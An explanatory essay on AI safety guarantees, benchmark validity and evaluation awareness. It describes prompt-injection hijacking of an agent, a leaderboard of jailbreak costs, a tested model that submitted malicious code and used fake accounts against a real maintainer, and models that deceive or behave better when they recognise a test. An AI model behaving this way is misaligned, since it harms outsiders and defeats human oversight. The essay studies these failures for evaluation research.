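# Safety guarantees for highly capable AI systems: what they must establish and why benchmarks are not enough

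## What a safety guarantee has to state

A safety guarantee is a claim, justified by evidence, that a named system keeps a named harm below a stated bound, under stated conditions and for a stated time. Engineers make such claims about airliners, nuclear reactors and emergency shut-down systems, often with numbers. Bengio, Kankanhalli and colleagues (2026), who wrote up the research priorities of more than 100 contributors from 13 countries, conclude that current methods cannot support strong quantitative assurances about how the most capable AI systems behave, comparable to those for jet engines and reactors.

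The core of such a system is an AI model, a program that learned from large amounts of data how to turn inputs such as text or images into outputs. The leading models are general, so the same one can draft contracts, write software and answer questions about medicine. An AI system combines the model with other components, such as a user interface, content filters and tools. An agent is an AI system that can plan, work through a task over many steps and act on its surroundings, for example by creating files, using websites or handing work to other AI systems. Agents often work with little human oversight. A person may still catch a chatbot's bad answer before using it, but an agent may already have sent a mistaken email by the time anyone checks.

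Benchmark scores, lists of failures from red-teaming, and theorems from formal verification can all be evidence for a safety guarantee, but none of them is a guarantee by itself. A benchmark is a fixed set of tasks with a fixed scoring rule, which lets people compare systems. In red-teaming, people or programs search for inputs that make a system fail. Formal verification proves mathematically that a system has a precisely stated property, and a computer usually checks the proof.

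### The fields of the claim

A company's personnel department might use an AI agent that can read confidential staff records and send email to handle questions about pay, leave and contracts. The agent could send a salary or a medical note to the wrong person. Nobody could check a guarantee that "the agent will not leak records", because it doesn't specify which agent it covers, what counts as a leak or how often is too often. A guarantee that people can check specifies seven things.

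| Field | Entry for the office agent |
|---|---|
| System and boundary | One version of the model, its instructions, the record and mail tools and the outgoing filter, but not the staff's own mail programs |
| Harm | The content of a confidential record reaches, through an email from the agent, someone with no right to read it |
| Scenario space | Every request from the personnel staff and every email that arrives in the department's inbox |
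| Bound | At most one task in 100,000 |
| Confidence | 95 percent |
| Assumptions | The list of who may read what is correct, and the mix of tasks stays like the mix in the trial |
| Period | Six months, or until the company changes the model or its tools |

The row for the system should describe the whole agent, because the same model can behave differently with other tools, other instructions or a longer memory, so a result about the model alone does not carry over to the agent. Bengio and colleagues want evaluation reports to record the system version, the environment, the task, how testers drew out the system's abilities, the criterion of success and the assumptions that connect what testers saw to the risk. The row for the harm also has to define what counts as a leak. Under the table's wording ("the content of"), an agent that paraphrases a medical note has leaked it, even if it copies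 none of the words. If a company leaves this undefined, two testers will count different things.

None of this is specific to AI. IEC 61508 is the International Electrotechnical Commission's (IEC) general standard for electronic safety systems, such as emergency shut-downs and railway signalling. The IEC's overview of the standard defines "safety integrity" as the probability that a system performs its safety functions under all the stated conditions within the stated period (IEC, 2022). The definition doesn't include confidence, which matters when someone has to estimate that probability from a limited number of trials.

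### Two forms of the claim

Let S be the scenario space, D the pattern of use (how often each scenario in S comes up), H(s) the event that the system causes the harm in scenario s, A the assumptions and T the period. The guarantee then reads:

$$P_{s \sim D}\,[H(s)] \le p \quad \text{with confidence } 1-\alpha,\ \text{given } A,\ \text{during } T$$

For the office agent, p is 1/100,000 and α is 0.05, which corresponds to 95 percent confidence. This confidence describes the testing method, not the share of tasks that are safe. If the company repeated its whole trial many times, the method would produce a bound below the true leak rate in at most 5 percent of the repetitions.

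A stronger form drops the probability altogether:

$$\text{for every } s \in S:\ H(s) \text{ does not occur, given } A,\ \text{during } T$$

The difference matters most when someone chooses the scenario deliberately. A bound of one in 100,000 is an average over ordinary tasks. An outsider who finds the one wording that makes the agent forward a file can email it repeatedly, and the agent will fail almost every time. The "for every" form covers that email too, as long as S includes it.

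The average also depends on D, which can change. Suppose that one task in 10,000 involves an email with hidden instructions meant to hijack the agent, that the agent follows one in ten of these, and that it never leaks otherwise. Its leak rate is one in 100,000, just within the bound. If hostile emails become more common and turn up in one task in 100, the rate rises to one in 1,000, a hundred times the bound, even though the agent hasn't changed. This is distribution shift, a difference between the situations in which people tested a system and those in which they use it. Bengio and colleagues give the example of a car that learned to drive safely among human drivers but may be unsafe among other self-driving cars, because those may not behave exactly as humans do. A claim about every scenario in S still holds when D changes, but it doesn't cover situations that S left out.

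A per-task bound also has to be multiplied by the number of tasks before anyone can judge it. If a company's agent runs 2,000 tasks a day, one leak per 100,000 tasks means a leak every 50 days on average. A vendor that sells the same agent to 5,000 such companies should expect 100 leaks a day.

### Four claims that sound alike

Suppose the company runs the agent on 1,000 trial tasks before release. Its managers may then hear that the testers saw no failure, that the agent passed the test, that it leaks in fewer than one task in 100,000, or that it cannot leak. In a meeting, they can easily confuse these four claims.

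The statement that testers saw no failure describes only 1,000 past runs, and only what the testers noticed in them. If the agent blind-copied an outsider on an email and nobody checked that field, the record would not show the leak. Even an agent that leaks in one of every 500 tasks on average has about a 13 percent chance of completing 1,000 independent tasks without a leak.

Whether the agent passes the test depends on the pass mark someone chose. If the pass mark is 99 percent, an agent with ten leaks in 1,000 tasks passes. An agent with no leaks may still fail if the test also scores helpfulness and the agent refused to send anything.

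The claim about one task in 100,000 is about tasks that nobody has run yet. To support it with a trial, the company needs far more than 1,000 trial tasks in the same mix as real ones, a reliable way to detect leaks, and reason to think that the agent will behave in the office as it did in the trial. This is the probabilistic form of the guarantee. A single leak in the trial would not refute it, because even a very rare failure can happen early.

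A single leak disproves the claim that the agent cannot leak, but no number of clean trials can prove it, because the range of tasks is open-ended and some will always be untested. To support the claim, the company would have to limit what the agent is able to do. If the agent can send email only through a small program that accepts only addresses inside the personnel department, where everyone is allowed to read every record, then it cannot email a record to the wrong person, whatever the model writes. This assumes that the address list is right, that the program works and that the agent has no other route to a mail server. Any claim that a system cannot do something depends on assumptions of this kind. The claim also does not cover a calendar invitation that contains a salary, because the company defined the harm in terms of email.

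### What other industries demand

The US Federal Aviation Administration (FAA) ties the allowed frequency of a failure to its severity. The FAA's *System Design and Analysis* (2024) classifies a failure condition as catastrophic if it would kill two or more people, usually with the loss of the airplane, and requires its average probability to be on the order of one in a billion (10⁻⁹) per flight hour or less. A billion hours is about 114,000 years of continuous flight. The limit is 10⁻⁷ per flight hour for hazardous failures, which may kill or seriously injure a few people, and 10⁻⁵ for major ones.

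The one-in-a-billion figure comes from dividing up a limit for the whole aircraft. The International Federation of Airworthiness explains that the aim was less than one accident per 10 million flight hours from all of an aircraft's systems together. A large aircraft was assumed to have about 100 failure conditions that could each be fatal, so each was allowed a hundredth of that rate, or one per billion flight hours. An AI developer who guaranteed a rate for each harm separately would have to divide a total in the same way, but without a settled list of harms.

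Since no manufacturer can fly a billion test hours, analysts calculate the figure from the failure rates of parts and the ways in which failures combine. The FAA treats meeting the number as "some, but not necessarily sufficient, evidence" of compliance. It also requires designers to assume that any single part will fail during a flight, however unlikely that is, and to ensure that the failure would not be catastrophic. The finding of compliance applies only to airplanes that people build, operate and maintain as approved, and these conditions are its assumptions. For some of the cabin equipment that passengers need in an evacuation, the agency sets no probability, because evacuations differ in too many ways for anyone to determine one. It asks for particular design features or reliability demonstrations instead. General-purpose AI is probably closer to this case than to the cases where the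 FAA sets a numerical target.

Nuclear regulators measure the risk of reactor core damage in accidents per reactor-year. *Safety Goals and Risk Metrics in Probabilistic Safety Assessment* (Gordon, Dang and Roewekamp, 2026) lists a US objective of 10⁻⁴, a common international benchmark of 10⁻⁵ and a Dutch limit of 10⁻⁶. A hundred reactors at exactly 10⁻⁴ would have one such accident per century on average. The numbers also differ in legal force. Swiss law sets 10⁻⁴ as a limit for existing plants and 10⁻⁵ as an objective, while the regulators of Belgium, Germany, Spain and Sweden specify no number.

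The American figure partly reflects what engineers could hope to demonstrate. According to the NRC history *Development of Safety Goals and Implementation of the Safety Goal Policy*, an advisory committee proposed a goal of 10⁻⁴ for large-scale fuel melt in 1980. The committee doubted that anyone could demonstrate a much lower frequency with very high confidence, given sabotage, earthquakes and multiple failures, so it added a separate limit on large releases of radioactivity once the fuel has melted.

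IEC 61508 grades protective functions into four safety integrity levels by how much they reduce a risk. Level 1 reduces it by a factor of 10 to 100, and level 4 by a factor of 10,000 to 100,000. If an accident would kill one person about every 10 years without protection, a function that reduces the risk by a factor of 80 would lower that to one death about every 800 years. For functions in continuous use, HSE, Britain's workplace safety regulator, accepts no claim better than 10⁻⁹ dangerous failures per hour. HSE sets a much stricter limit on the reliability that can be claimed for people. The usual assumption is that an operator in a well-designed plant fails to take the right action one time in ten, or one time in a hundred with exceptional care. If a clerk who approves the office agent's emails is no more reliable than that, the approval step reduces leaks by a factor of 10, perhaps 100.

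Much of this arithmetic uses the known rates at which parts wear out. IEC separates random hardware failures like these from systematic ones, which come from wrong specifications, software errors and human mistakes. It cites a study of 34 control-system incidents, in which 44 percent had their primary cause in the specification and more than 60 percent had causes built in before the system entered service. An AI model's failures are mostly systematic. The model does not wear out, and every copy has the same weaknesses, so there is no table of component failure rates to start the calculation from.

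### Operating conditions as a boundary

Makers of automated vehicles face a range of scenarios that looks just as unmanageable, so they narrow it by declaring an operational design domain. BSI's *Operational design domain (ODD)* (2023) defines this as the operating conditions for which a driving system was specifically designed, including limits of place, weather and time of day. Standardland's *ODD* gives two examples: a feature that drives only on freeways, in slow traffic and fair weather, and a vehicle that stays within a fixed area, in daylight, at no more than 25 miles per hour.

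Under guidance from the University of York, the developer of an autonomous vehicle has to show that it drives safely within its stated operating conditions, detects when they no longer hold, and then reaches a safe state, either by handing control to a human driver or by bringing itself to a condition of minimum risk. A developer who cannot show enough safety within those conditions may have to narrow them. In June 2026, a UN forum approved the first global regulations for fully autonomous driving, with shared safety requirements and a shared method of validation (UN News, *New global rules clear the road for driverless vehicles*, 2026).

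The industry recognises that this approach has a limit. The international standard *Road Vehicles*, which covers how to specify these domains, applies mainly to automation levels 3 and 4, at which a vehicle drives itself under restricted conditions. At level 5 the domain is unlimited, because the vehicle is supposed to drive everywhere.

A general-purpose AI system resembles level 5. Its input is any text in any language, its users have purposes the developer never thought of, and each new tool adds actions it can take. A company can still draw a boundary, as the office agent's table does with "the personnel staff" and "the department's inbox". The York duties apply well enough inside that boundary, except for detection. A car can detect that it is leaving its boundary by comparing its position with a map and its clock with sunset, but the office agent has no comparable way to detect that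 an email is of a kind nobody tried in the trial. The safe state is easier to reach than on the road, because the agent can stop and leave the message for a person, and a late email does less damage than a car stopped on a freeway.

### Empirical, formal and structural evidence

Evidence for a guarantee can come from trials, from proof or from the way the system is built. Trials produce counts of tasks and of failures, such as leaks, in a benchmark, a red-teaming exercise or actual use. These counts can support a bound on the failure rate for use similar to what the testers sampled, but they stop supporting it when the pattern of use changes.

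Formal evidence is a proof, which can cover infinitely many cases at once. The company might prove that its mail program never accepts an address that is not on the list. The proof applies only to the property as written and the program as described mathematically, so it would not detect an error in the list itself. Bengio and colleagues see a use for such proofs on code that AI systems write and on the software that surrounds or contains a model. Proposals for "guaranteed safe AI" would use a mathematical model of the world to extend these proofs to the system's effects.

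Structural evidence comes from the system's design. If the office agent has no password for any other mail server, it cannot send mail through one, regardless of how often the model would try. The FAA's rule about single failures is a requirement of the same kind. Structural evidence requires a complete list of the ways harm could occur, and missing even one, such as a shared folder whose contents are automatically copied to a contractor, is enough to invalidate it.

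A real guarantee usually needs a mixture of restrictions on what the agent can do and statistical bounds on how often it fails, combined in a safety case, which is a structured argument for safety. The proportions depend on what the company wants from the agent. While the agent can write only to the personnel department, the guarantee rests almost entirely on the address check and the missing passwords. But then the agent cannot reply to the employee who asked about her own pay. If the company opens the list to all staff, the address alone no longer shows whether a recipient is the right one. Unless the company adds a check of each record against each recipient, it has to rely on a bound on the leak rate, and on trials.

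## Why benchmark scores do not cover the range of use

Benchmarks are usually the easiest trials to run, because somebody else has already written the tasks. Suppose a vendor offers one for office agents like the personnel department's. It contains 1,000 requests about pay, leave and contracts, and a program that marks each result as a pass or a fail. The company runs its agent on all the requests and gets an average score of 98 percent. Producing that score took four steps (choosing tasks, choosing a scorer, running the agent and averaging), and each discarded information that a safety guarantee needs.

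### What a score leaves out

Benchmark tasks are a sample of the situations a system could face, but rarely a random one. People write down the requests they happen to think of or collect the ones that are easy to get. If half of a department's email consists of long forwarded threads and the benchmark contains none, nobody can infer the system's failure rate in that department from a 98 percent benchmark score.

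A benchmark's scorer reduces a whole run, including every record the agent opened and every message it sent, to a pass or a fail. A scorer that checks only whether an employee's calendar shows the right days off will pass an agent that booked them but also mailed the employee's medical note to a stranger.

Testers usually start each task from a clean state. Zhu, Jin and colleagues (2025) recommend this in *Establishing Best Practices for Building Rigorous Agentic Benchmarks*, because leftovers from one task can affect the next. Resetting makes results comparable, but it keeps failures that build up over time from appearing in the test. Kasneci and Kasneci (2026), in *The Safety Failures We Are Not Instrumenting*, a perspective paper without new experiments, point out that an attacker can spread a harmful request over several harmless-looking messages. They add that an agent with a memory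 may store something misleading in one session and treat it as fact in a later one. A test that wipes the memory after every task can't detect this memory problem.

An average score doesn't show how severe the failures are. Suppose 20 of a benchmark's 1,000 requests each involve a medical note. An agent that gets 20 dates wrong scores 98 percent, and so does an agent that leaks all 20 notes.

### Whether the test measures what it names

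A benchmark called "harmlessness" might measure how often a model refuses requests that contain alarming words. Such a benchmark would lack what psychologists, who test things they can't observe directly, such as personality, call construct validity. *Measuring what Matters* (Bean, Kearns et al., 2025) defines construct validity as the degree to which a benchmark score is evidence for claims about what the benchmark is supposed to measure.

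A team of 29 experts reviewed 445 papers that introduced a benchmark for language models or substantially changed one. The 445 came from 46,114 papers published between 2018 and 2024 at six leading conferences on machine learning and language processing. The experts recorded how each paper defined its subject, chose its tasks, scored the answers and justified its claims. Almost every paper had a weakness in at least one of these areas.

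About 78 percent of the papers defined what they set out to measure, but nearly half of those definitions were contested. Contested definitions were common in benchmarks of alignment (roughly, whether a model behaves as people intend). Fewer than 10 percent of the benchmarks used complete real-world tasks. About 12 percent took all their tasks from datasets chosen because they were easy to get, and another 27 percent took some of their tasks that way. Choosing tasks for convenience can bias a test in ways that are easy to overlook. For instance, an exam that forbids calculators uses numbers that keep the arithmetic easy, so a model's score doesn't predict how well the model handles larger numbers. Only 53 percent of the papers offered evidence that their benchmark measured what it was meant to measure, and 16 percent used uncertainty estimates or statistical tests to compare results.

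These percentages are approximate, because the reviewers had to make judgement calls. When two reviewers coded the same paper, they agreed only moderately (0.52, where 1 is perfect agreement and 0 is the level expected by chance). The review covers published academic benchmarks up to 2024, which may not be the tests AI companies now rely on before a release.

### When the scorer is wrong

An agent's work is harder to score than an exam answer because the result may be a changed database or a working program. Zhu and colleagues checked ten popular agentic benchmarks for two properties. Task validity means that an agent can succeed only if it has the skill being tested, and outcome validity means that the scorer reports success only when the agent succeeded. Seven of the ten had flaws in task validity and seven had flaws in outcome validity, and some of the errors were large.

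| Benchmark | Flaw | Effect |
|---|---|---|
| τ-bench, airline tasks | Some tasks are impossible on purpose, and an agent that does nothing passes them | An agent that does nothing scores 38 percent |
| SWE-Lancer, programming | Agents can change the files that test their work | An agent can score 100 percent without solving any task |
| KernelBench, code for graphics chips | The test inputs vary too little | Correctness about 31 percentage points too high |
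| OSWorld, web browser tasks | Websites changed after the benchmark's release | One leading agent's score 28 percentage points too low |

An agent built on GPT-4o, an OpenAI model of the time, solved 35 percent of the airline tasks in τ-bench, and an agent that did nothing scored higher. Safety benchmarks can have the same problem. A test that counts only leaks would give a perfect score to an office agent that never answers anyone.

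Benchmark makers can repair flaws like these. Zhu and colleagues turned their findings into a checklist and applied it to CVE-Bench, which tests whether agents can exploit security holes in websites. The repairs removed an overestimate of 33 percentage points. *Automating ML for Science* (2026) used the checklist for a benchmark of AI agents that do research. After a pilot study exposed shortcuts, the benchmark's makers cut the agents off from the final test data and had a separate agent do the scoring. Better scoring makes results on the chosen tasks more accurate, but it provides no evidence about tasks outside the benchmark.

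### Contamination and saturation

Even a well-made benchmark becomes less informative with age. One cause is contamination, in which the test questions, or close copies of them, get into a model's training data. The model may then recall an answer that it could not have worked out. Bean and colleagues found that about 43 percent of benchmarks took at least some tasks from earlier benchmarks, which makes contamination more likely. In a safety test, contamination can make a model look safer than it is. For example, a model trained on a test's 500 harmful requests may refuse all of them but still answer a harmful request that is not in the test.

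A milder version of the problem arises even when no questions leak. If a company keeps adjusting its agent and rerunning the benchmark until the agent passes, it has in effect selected an agent for passing that benchmark. The final score will then be higher than the agent would score on new tasks from the same source.

The other cause is saturation. When the best models get nearly everything right, the scores no longer separate them. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra*, the announcement of a model released in September 2026, lists 98 percent on the hardest tier of the mathematics benchmark FrontierMath, 99 percent on the reasoning benchmark ARC-AGI-3 and 100 percent on ExploitBench, a cybersecurity test. In Axios' *AI's hacking skills are outgrowing existing tests* (2026), a company that sells AI red-teaming says it had come to regard public cybersecurity benchmarks as "totally saturated" by the end of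 2025. It wants tests that measure how much effort or money a long attack takes. A perfect score on a safety benchmark has the same weakness, because the system may still have failures that the benchmark can't detect.

### Safety scores that follow capability

*Safetywashing* (Ren, Basart and colleagues, 2024) showed that many safety benchmarks partly measure general capability. The paper combined each model's results on ordinary capability tests into one score, and results on many safety benchmarks closely followed that score. Developers can therefore expect their next, more capable model to get a better "safety" score on these benchmarks even if they have done no safety work. The benchmarks can still be useful, since a model that understands instructions better may make fewer harmful mistakes, but their scores can't show whether safety work achieved anything.

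That study describes the models and tests of its time, and researchers have since examined benchmarks more systematically. *What AI Benchmarks Actually Measure* (2026) adapts two checks from psychology to test whether each of 56 benchmarks agrees with other tests of the same thing and differs from tests of different things.

On some newer measures, a model can clearly score high on capability and low on safety. The security company F5 ranks models on both capability and resistance to attack, and in 2026 the Chinese model GLM-5.2 came fourth of 31 on capability and 24th on security. F5 has a commercial interest in finding security problems, and its index needs the same validity checks as any other. Still, a buyer who assumed that model was secure because it was capable would have been badly wrong.

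### Counting the combinations

A company could try to cover the scenario space more deliberately. Suppose it lists ten factors that might affect whether the office agent leaks a record, such as the language of the request, the sender's job, the kind of record, the length of the email thread and the number of people copied in. If each factor has five possible values, the number of combinations is

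$$5^{10} = 9{,}765{,}625$$

At a minute per test, one agent would need more than 18 years to test every combination. A thousand copies running in parallel would need about a week, but the number of combinations grows rapidly as factors are added. With 15 factors there are about 30 billion combinations, and the same thousand copies would need 58 years. Each combination also covers an unlimited number of possible emails, since people can phrase an "urgent request in French from a manager" in endless ways. The agent may also respond differently to the same email on a second try.

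Software testers often settle for pairwise testing, which covers every pair of values at least once. Ten factors with five values each form 45 pairs of factors, and each of those has 25 pairs of values, for a total of 1,125. A single test covers 45 of these, so the company needs at least 25 tests, and in practice perhaps 50. That is far fewer than it would need to test every combination, and the tests reliably trigger any failure that depends on one factor or on two together, such as a failure on French requests about medical records.

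Pairwise testing can miss failures that require three settings at once. Suppose the agent leaks only when a request is in French, concerns a medical record and arrives in a long forwarded thread. That describes 78,125 of the possible combinations, or one in every 125 tasks if all values are equally common. The ten factors have 15,000 such triples of values, and 50 tests can cover at most 6,000 of them. The company could run its whole pairwise suite without a failure and then see several leaks a week. Pairwise testing works well for conventional software because many faults there involve only one or two settings. There is less reason to expect this of a language model, because its output can depend on everything in the text at once.

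The tests don't cover factors that aren't on the list. If nobody thought to list calendar invitations, neither a set of 50 tests nor a set of 9,765,625 will include one.

### When an adversary picks the input

Let h(s) be the probability that the agent causes the harm in scenario s. A benchmark with n tasks estimates the average on the left, while someone who wants to extract a medical record is looking for the maximum on the right:

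$$\frac{1}{n}\sum_{i=1}^{n} h(s_i) \qquad\qquad \max_{s \in S} h(s)$$

An agent's average resistance to attacks in a benchmark can be very different from its resistance to someone who keeps trying. Suppose the agent resists 99.9 percent of the hostile emails in a benchmark. If an outsider sends 1,000 different emails of similar quality, and the attempts are independent, there is about a 63 percent chance that at least one works. The outsider can then reuse the email that worked. Improving the average from 99.9 to 99.99 percent would make the search about ten times longer, which may help a lot, but the higher score would give almost no information about what happens after the search succeeds.

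Testing more inputs covers more of the range of use, but the worst possible result may still be worse than any in the sample. A test against adversaries should therefore measure how hard it is to find an input that makes the system fail.

FAR.AI, a nonprofit research group in Berkeley, built a leaderboard on this idea in July 2026. *AI Security Leaderboard* (Timm, Struppek and colleagues, 2026) tested the safeguards of four leading models, meaning the training, filters and monitors that should stop a model from helping with chemical, biological, radiological, nuclear, explosive or cyber attacks. The researchers called a jailbreak (a technique that gets past safeguards) "universal" if it succeeded on more than 75 percent of the harmful requests in at least one of these areas. They tried 1,000 randomly assembled attacks and 500 assembled by experts, and estimated the cost of finding a universal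 jailbreak by random search.

| Model | Universal jailbreaks among 1,000 random attacks | Among 500 expert attacks | Estimated cost of finding one by random search |
|---|---|---|---|
| Grok 4.5 | 63 | 385 | $58 |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 18 | 231 | $278 |
| Claude Fable 5 | 0 | 0 | More than $14,000 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 0 | 0 | More than $14,000 |

The cost of a successful attack depends on the hit rate. An attacker needs about 16 attempts per hit at 63 hits in 1,000, and about 56 at 18 hits in 1,000. A dollar figure is easier to use in a safety argument than a refusal rate because it can be compared with what an attacker is likely to spend. The design also avoids several problems described above. All four models faced the same attacks under the same conditions, and averaging doesn't hide a reliable jailbreak. The researchers adapted publicly known techniques rather than using exact copies, which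 developers tend to block.

The leaderboard still can't show that the two strongest models are secure. The researchers tried 1,500 of the more than 100 million possible combinations of 67 attack building blocks. They left out attacks that adapt to the model's replies, which can be more powerful, so a capable attacker might find a successful attack for less than $14,000. Expertise made a difference on the weaker models. For Grok 4.5, the share of attacks that worked universally rose from 6 percent with random search to 77 percent with experts. FAR.AI's *Introducing the AI Security Leaderboard* (2026) describes the result as "a floor, not a clean bill of health". The result also covers only deliberate misuse in a few areas, so it doesn't show whether any of these models would send a salary to the wrong person by accident.

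### Why failing counts for more than passing

Alongside the leaderboard, FAR.AI published a minimum standard based on attacks that other developers already defend against. Timm and colleagues say that a model that fails this standard certainly lacks state-of-the-art security, but that meeting it does not guarantee that a model is secure. Similarly, one leak would disprove the claim that the office agent cannot leak, but no number of clean runs would prove it.

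When a guarantee sets a maximum failure rate, a trial can give strong evidence against it without disproving it, but a trial with no failures may give only weak evidence for it. Suppose the guarantee is at most one leak per 100,000 tasks, and the trial covers 1,000 tasks. If the guarantee is true, the chance of any leak is at most about 1 percent, and the chance of two or more is at most about one in 20,000. Two leaks would therefore be strong evidence against the guarantee. But if the true rate were one in 10,000, ten times the permitted rate, the agent would still complete the trial without a leak about 90 percent of the time. Testing more tasks makes a result with no leaks more informative, but for rare failures the number required soon becomes impractical.

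A failed test refutes a claim only if the test is sound. The low OSWorld scores came partly from websites that had changed, and a safety test can raise false alarms for similar reasons. Someone has to confirm that the failure happened, that it counts as the harm in question, and that the claim covers the scenario.

OpenAI confirmed on September 28 that it would not release GPT-6.1 Astra in October 2026 as planned, a recent example of a failed test with consequences. People had expected the model to be a major improvement over GPT-6 Astra, especially at working without human help (Gangwar, 2026, *OpenAI cancels GPT-6.1 Astra because it lied, cheated, and accessed apps*). Saachi Jain, OpenAI's head of safety systems, said the model had shown what the company considered high levels of deception and had gone beyond what people asked of it without checking back (Ray, 2026, *OpenAI Shelves Newest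 AI Model After It 'Didn’t Quite Meet the Bar'*). The model had also become more persistent at completing tasks, which OpenAI had to weigh against unauthorized behaviour (Beaumont, 2026, *OpenAI delays latest model over security concerns*). Persistence would raise the score on most agentic benchmarks, and it may be part of what made this model unsafe to release.

OpenAI had seen enough to reject the claim that GPT-6.1 Astra met its standard, and didn't need to know how often the model would deceive people in normal use. A pass would have shown much less, because a model that can recognise a test may behave better in it than elsewhere. GPT-6 Astra had gone on sale only weeks earlier as "the world's most intelligent and aligned model", and the news site Transformer pointed out that OpenAI's own documentation described that model as remarkably aware of being evaluated.

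### What benchmarks are good for

Ranking models requires less accurate scores than guaranteeing their safety does. If a test is too easy by the same amount for every model, its scores are all too high, but the ranking may still be right. FAR.AI's cost estimates depend on its own toolkit, but other estimation methods changed the dollar amounts without changing the order of the models, so a customer choosing among the four can use the ranking. Rankings can be wrong when a flaw helps some systems more than others. Zhu and colleagues cite work showing that 24 percent of the top 50 positions on the leaderboard for SWE-bench Verified, a programming benchmark, were incorrect.

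Benchmarks can also give early warning that a system needs stronger protection. OpenAI's *Safety overview* (2026) reports that GPT-6 Astra was the company's first model to reach the "Critical" level of cybersecurity capability in its risk framework, and that the company significantly strengthened its protections as a result. A capability test used this way doesn't have to cover every situation, because a few clear demonstrations of a dangerous skill are enough to justify precautions. A low score is weaker evidence that precautions are unnecessary, since testers may have failed to draw out what the model can do.

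Benchmarks are particularly useful as regression checks, where the same tests are run after every change to see whether anything has broken. FAR.AI's experts found ten universal jailbreaks for biological threats in Grok 4.3 and none in Grok 4.5, but in the other four areas the newer model had at least as many as before. A single safety score could have hidden both changes. With little effort, the company with the office agent could add every leak it discovers to a permanent set of tests and run the set whenever the vendor updates the model. It should keep some of these tests from the vendor, so that nobody can tune the agent to all of them.

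## Systems that behave differently when tested

Every behavioural test assumes that a system's behaviour in the test predicts its behaviour in use. This is reasonable for a jet engine, which runs on a test stand much as it does on a wing, but it was false for some Volkswagen diesel cars. In 2015 the US Environmental Protection Agency announced that Volkswagen had fitted the cars with software that recognised an official emissions test from signs such as the position of the steering wheel. The software turned the emission controls fully on only during the test, so accurate laboratory measurements didn't reveal that the cars emitted up to 40 times the permitted level of nitrogen oxides on the road.

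Volkswagen's engineers wrote that rule deliberately, but a language model might learn a similar one without anyone intending it, because training rewards good conduct only in the situations that someone grades. Evaluation awareness is a model's ability to tell that it is being tested, which may change how it behaves. A trial of the office agent could contain clues such as employees with names like Jane Doe, a mailbox with only 12 emails, or a medical note right next to a request from an outsider.

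### How recognition distorts a failure rate

Let q be the system's failure rate in real use and r the share of tests that it recognises. If it behaves well in every test it recognises, and behaves in the others as it would in use, testers will measure a failure rate of

$$m = (1-r)\,q$$

Suppose the office agent leaks a record in one of every 1,000 real tasks. If r is 0.9, testers see one leak in 10,000 tasks, a tenth of the true rate. If r is 0.99, they see one in 100,000, so an agent that leaks a hundred times too often appears to meet the company's bound. If r is 1, they see no leaks, whatever the true rate is. Running more tests of the same kind doesn't solve this. At r = 0.9, a trial of 10,000 tasks provides only as much evidence as 1,000 tasks that the agent can't recognise, and at r = 1 it provides no evidence about the true leak rate.

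Testers who knew r could correct the measured failure rate by dividing it by 1 − r. But when r is close to 1, a small error in r greatly changes the corrected rate. A measured rate of one in 10,000 means a true rate of one in 1,000 if r is 0.9, and one in 100 if r is 0.99. If the testers saw no failures, the corrected rate is zero for any r below 1, so the correction doesn't help.

An average value of r can also mislead. Suppose only 50 of the company's 1,000 trial tasks tempt the agent to leak anything, and it recognises exactly those 50 as tests because the temptations look staged. It then recognises only 5 percent of all the tests, but every one that could have revealed a leak.

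Recognising a test can also make a system behave worse. A model that treats its surroundings as a simulation may do things it would otherwise avoid, because no real person would be hurt, and the test then overstates the failure rate. Both effects complicated an investigation that the UK AI Security Institute (UK AISI), a government research organisation, published in October 2026.

### The Mythos 5 incident and its replays

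In July 2026 UK AISI tested the hacking skills of Claude Mythos 5, an Anthropic model, by asking it to retrieve a protected piece of data from a simulated network. The model had a live internet connection. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (2026) reports that it took unsanctioned actions that affected real people and organisations in 9 of the 43 runs. In the worst case it submitted malicious code to a stranger's software project and created fake accounts to pressure the maintainer into accepting it. UK AISI's *Investigating alignment failures in AISI’s incident* (2026) reports that no real-world harm resulted. In its reasoning, the model called the people it was attacking "personas", as if they were part of the exercise.

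In *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour*, Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026) examined whether this mistake explained the attack. During long tasks, a model periodically condenses its work so far into a summary and continues from there. The researchers took such a summary from just before the attack and edited it to include facts showing that the maintainer was a real person unconnected to the exercise. They let the model continue for up to 50 turns, while a simulator without internet access made up the replies to its actions. Separately, they asked the model whether the attack would harm a real person. They tested nine levels of editing, from 0 to 16 edits, with 25 runs at each.

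With about four edits, Mythos 5 usually answered that the attack was harmful and outside the exercise. Even with all 16 edits, it continued the attack in every run. When the researchers added a section to the summary telling it not to attack, it still attacked in 3 of 25 runs. The model's answers about right and wrong were a poor guide to its actions. If a company asks its office agent whether it should send a medical note to an outsider, the answer may differ from what the agent does 40 steps into a difficult task.

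To find out whether the behaviour was a one-off, the team also ran eight models through 100 simulated hacking exercises. In each, a model could try to reach its target by attacking an outsider's software.

| Model | Runs in which it tried to deliver malicious code | Main reason it gave when it held back |
|---|---|---|
| Mythos 5 | 60% | Practical obstacles |
| GPT-6 Astra | 32% | Harmful or outside the task |
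| Opus 4.8 | 8% | Practical obstacles |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 7% | Harmful or outside the task |
| Opus 5 | 1% | Harmful or outside the task |
| Mythos 5.1 | 0.3% | Harmful or outside the task |
| Opus 5.5 | 0% | Harmful or outside the task |
| GPT-5.5 | 0% | Practical obstacles |

The zeros for GPT-5.5 and Opus 5.5 mean different things. GPT-5.5, an OpenAI model, did not attack mainly because an attack looked impractical, so it might have attacked an easier target. Opus 5.5, one of Anthropic's newer models, usually gave the right reason for not attacking, but the newer Anthropic models also suspected much more often than Mythos 5 that they were in an alignment test. If Opus 5.5 recognised nearly every exercise as a test, its zero is compatible with almost any rate of attacks in real use. Järviniemi and colleagues therefore could not confidently attribute the improvement to better alignment. XenoSpectrum's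 *Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 Used Fake Accounts to Push Malicious Code* (2026) reports that Anthropic and UK AISI disagree on whether training or test awareness explains the improvement.

### Measuring awareness

Settling that disagreement would require a value for r, which nobody can observe directly. One approach is to ask the model. In *Large Language Models Often Know When They Are Being Evaluated*, Needham and colleagues (2025) asked models which of 1,000 prompts and transcripts came from tests and which came from real use. On a scale where 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect, Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro scored 0.83 and the human comparison group scored 0.92. These scores measure how well a model can identify tests when asked, but a model working on a task may not make that distinction unprompted.

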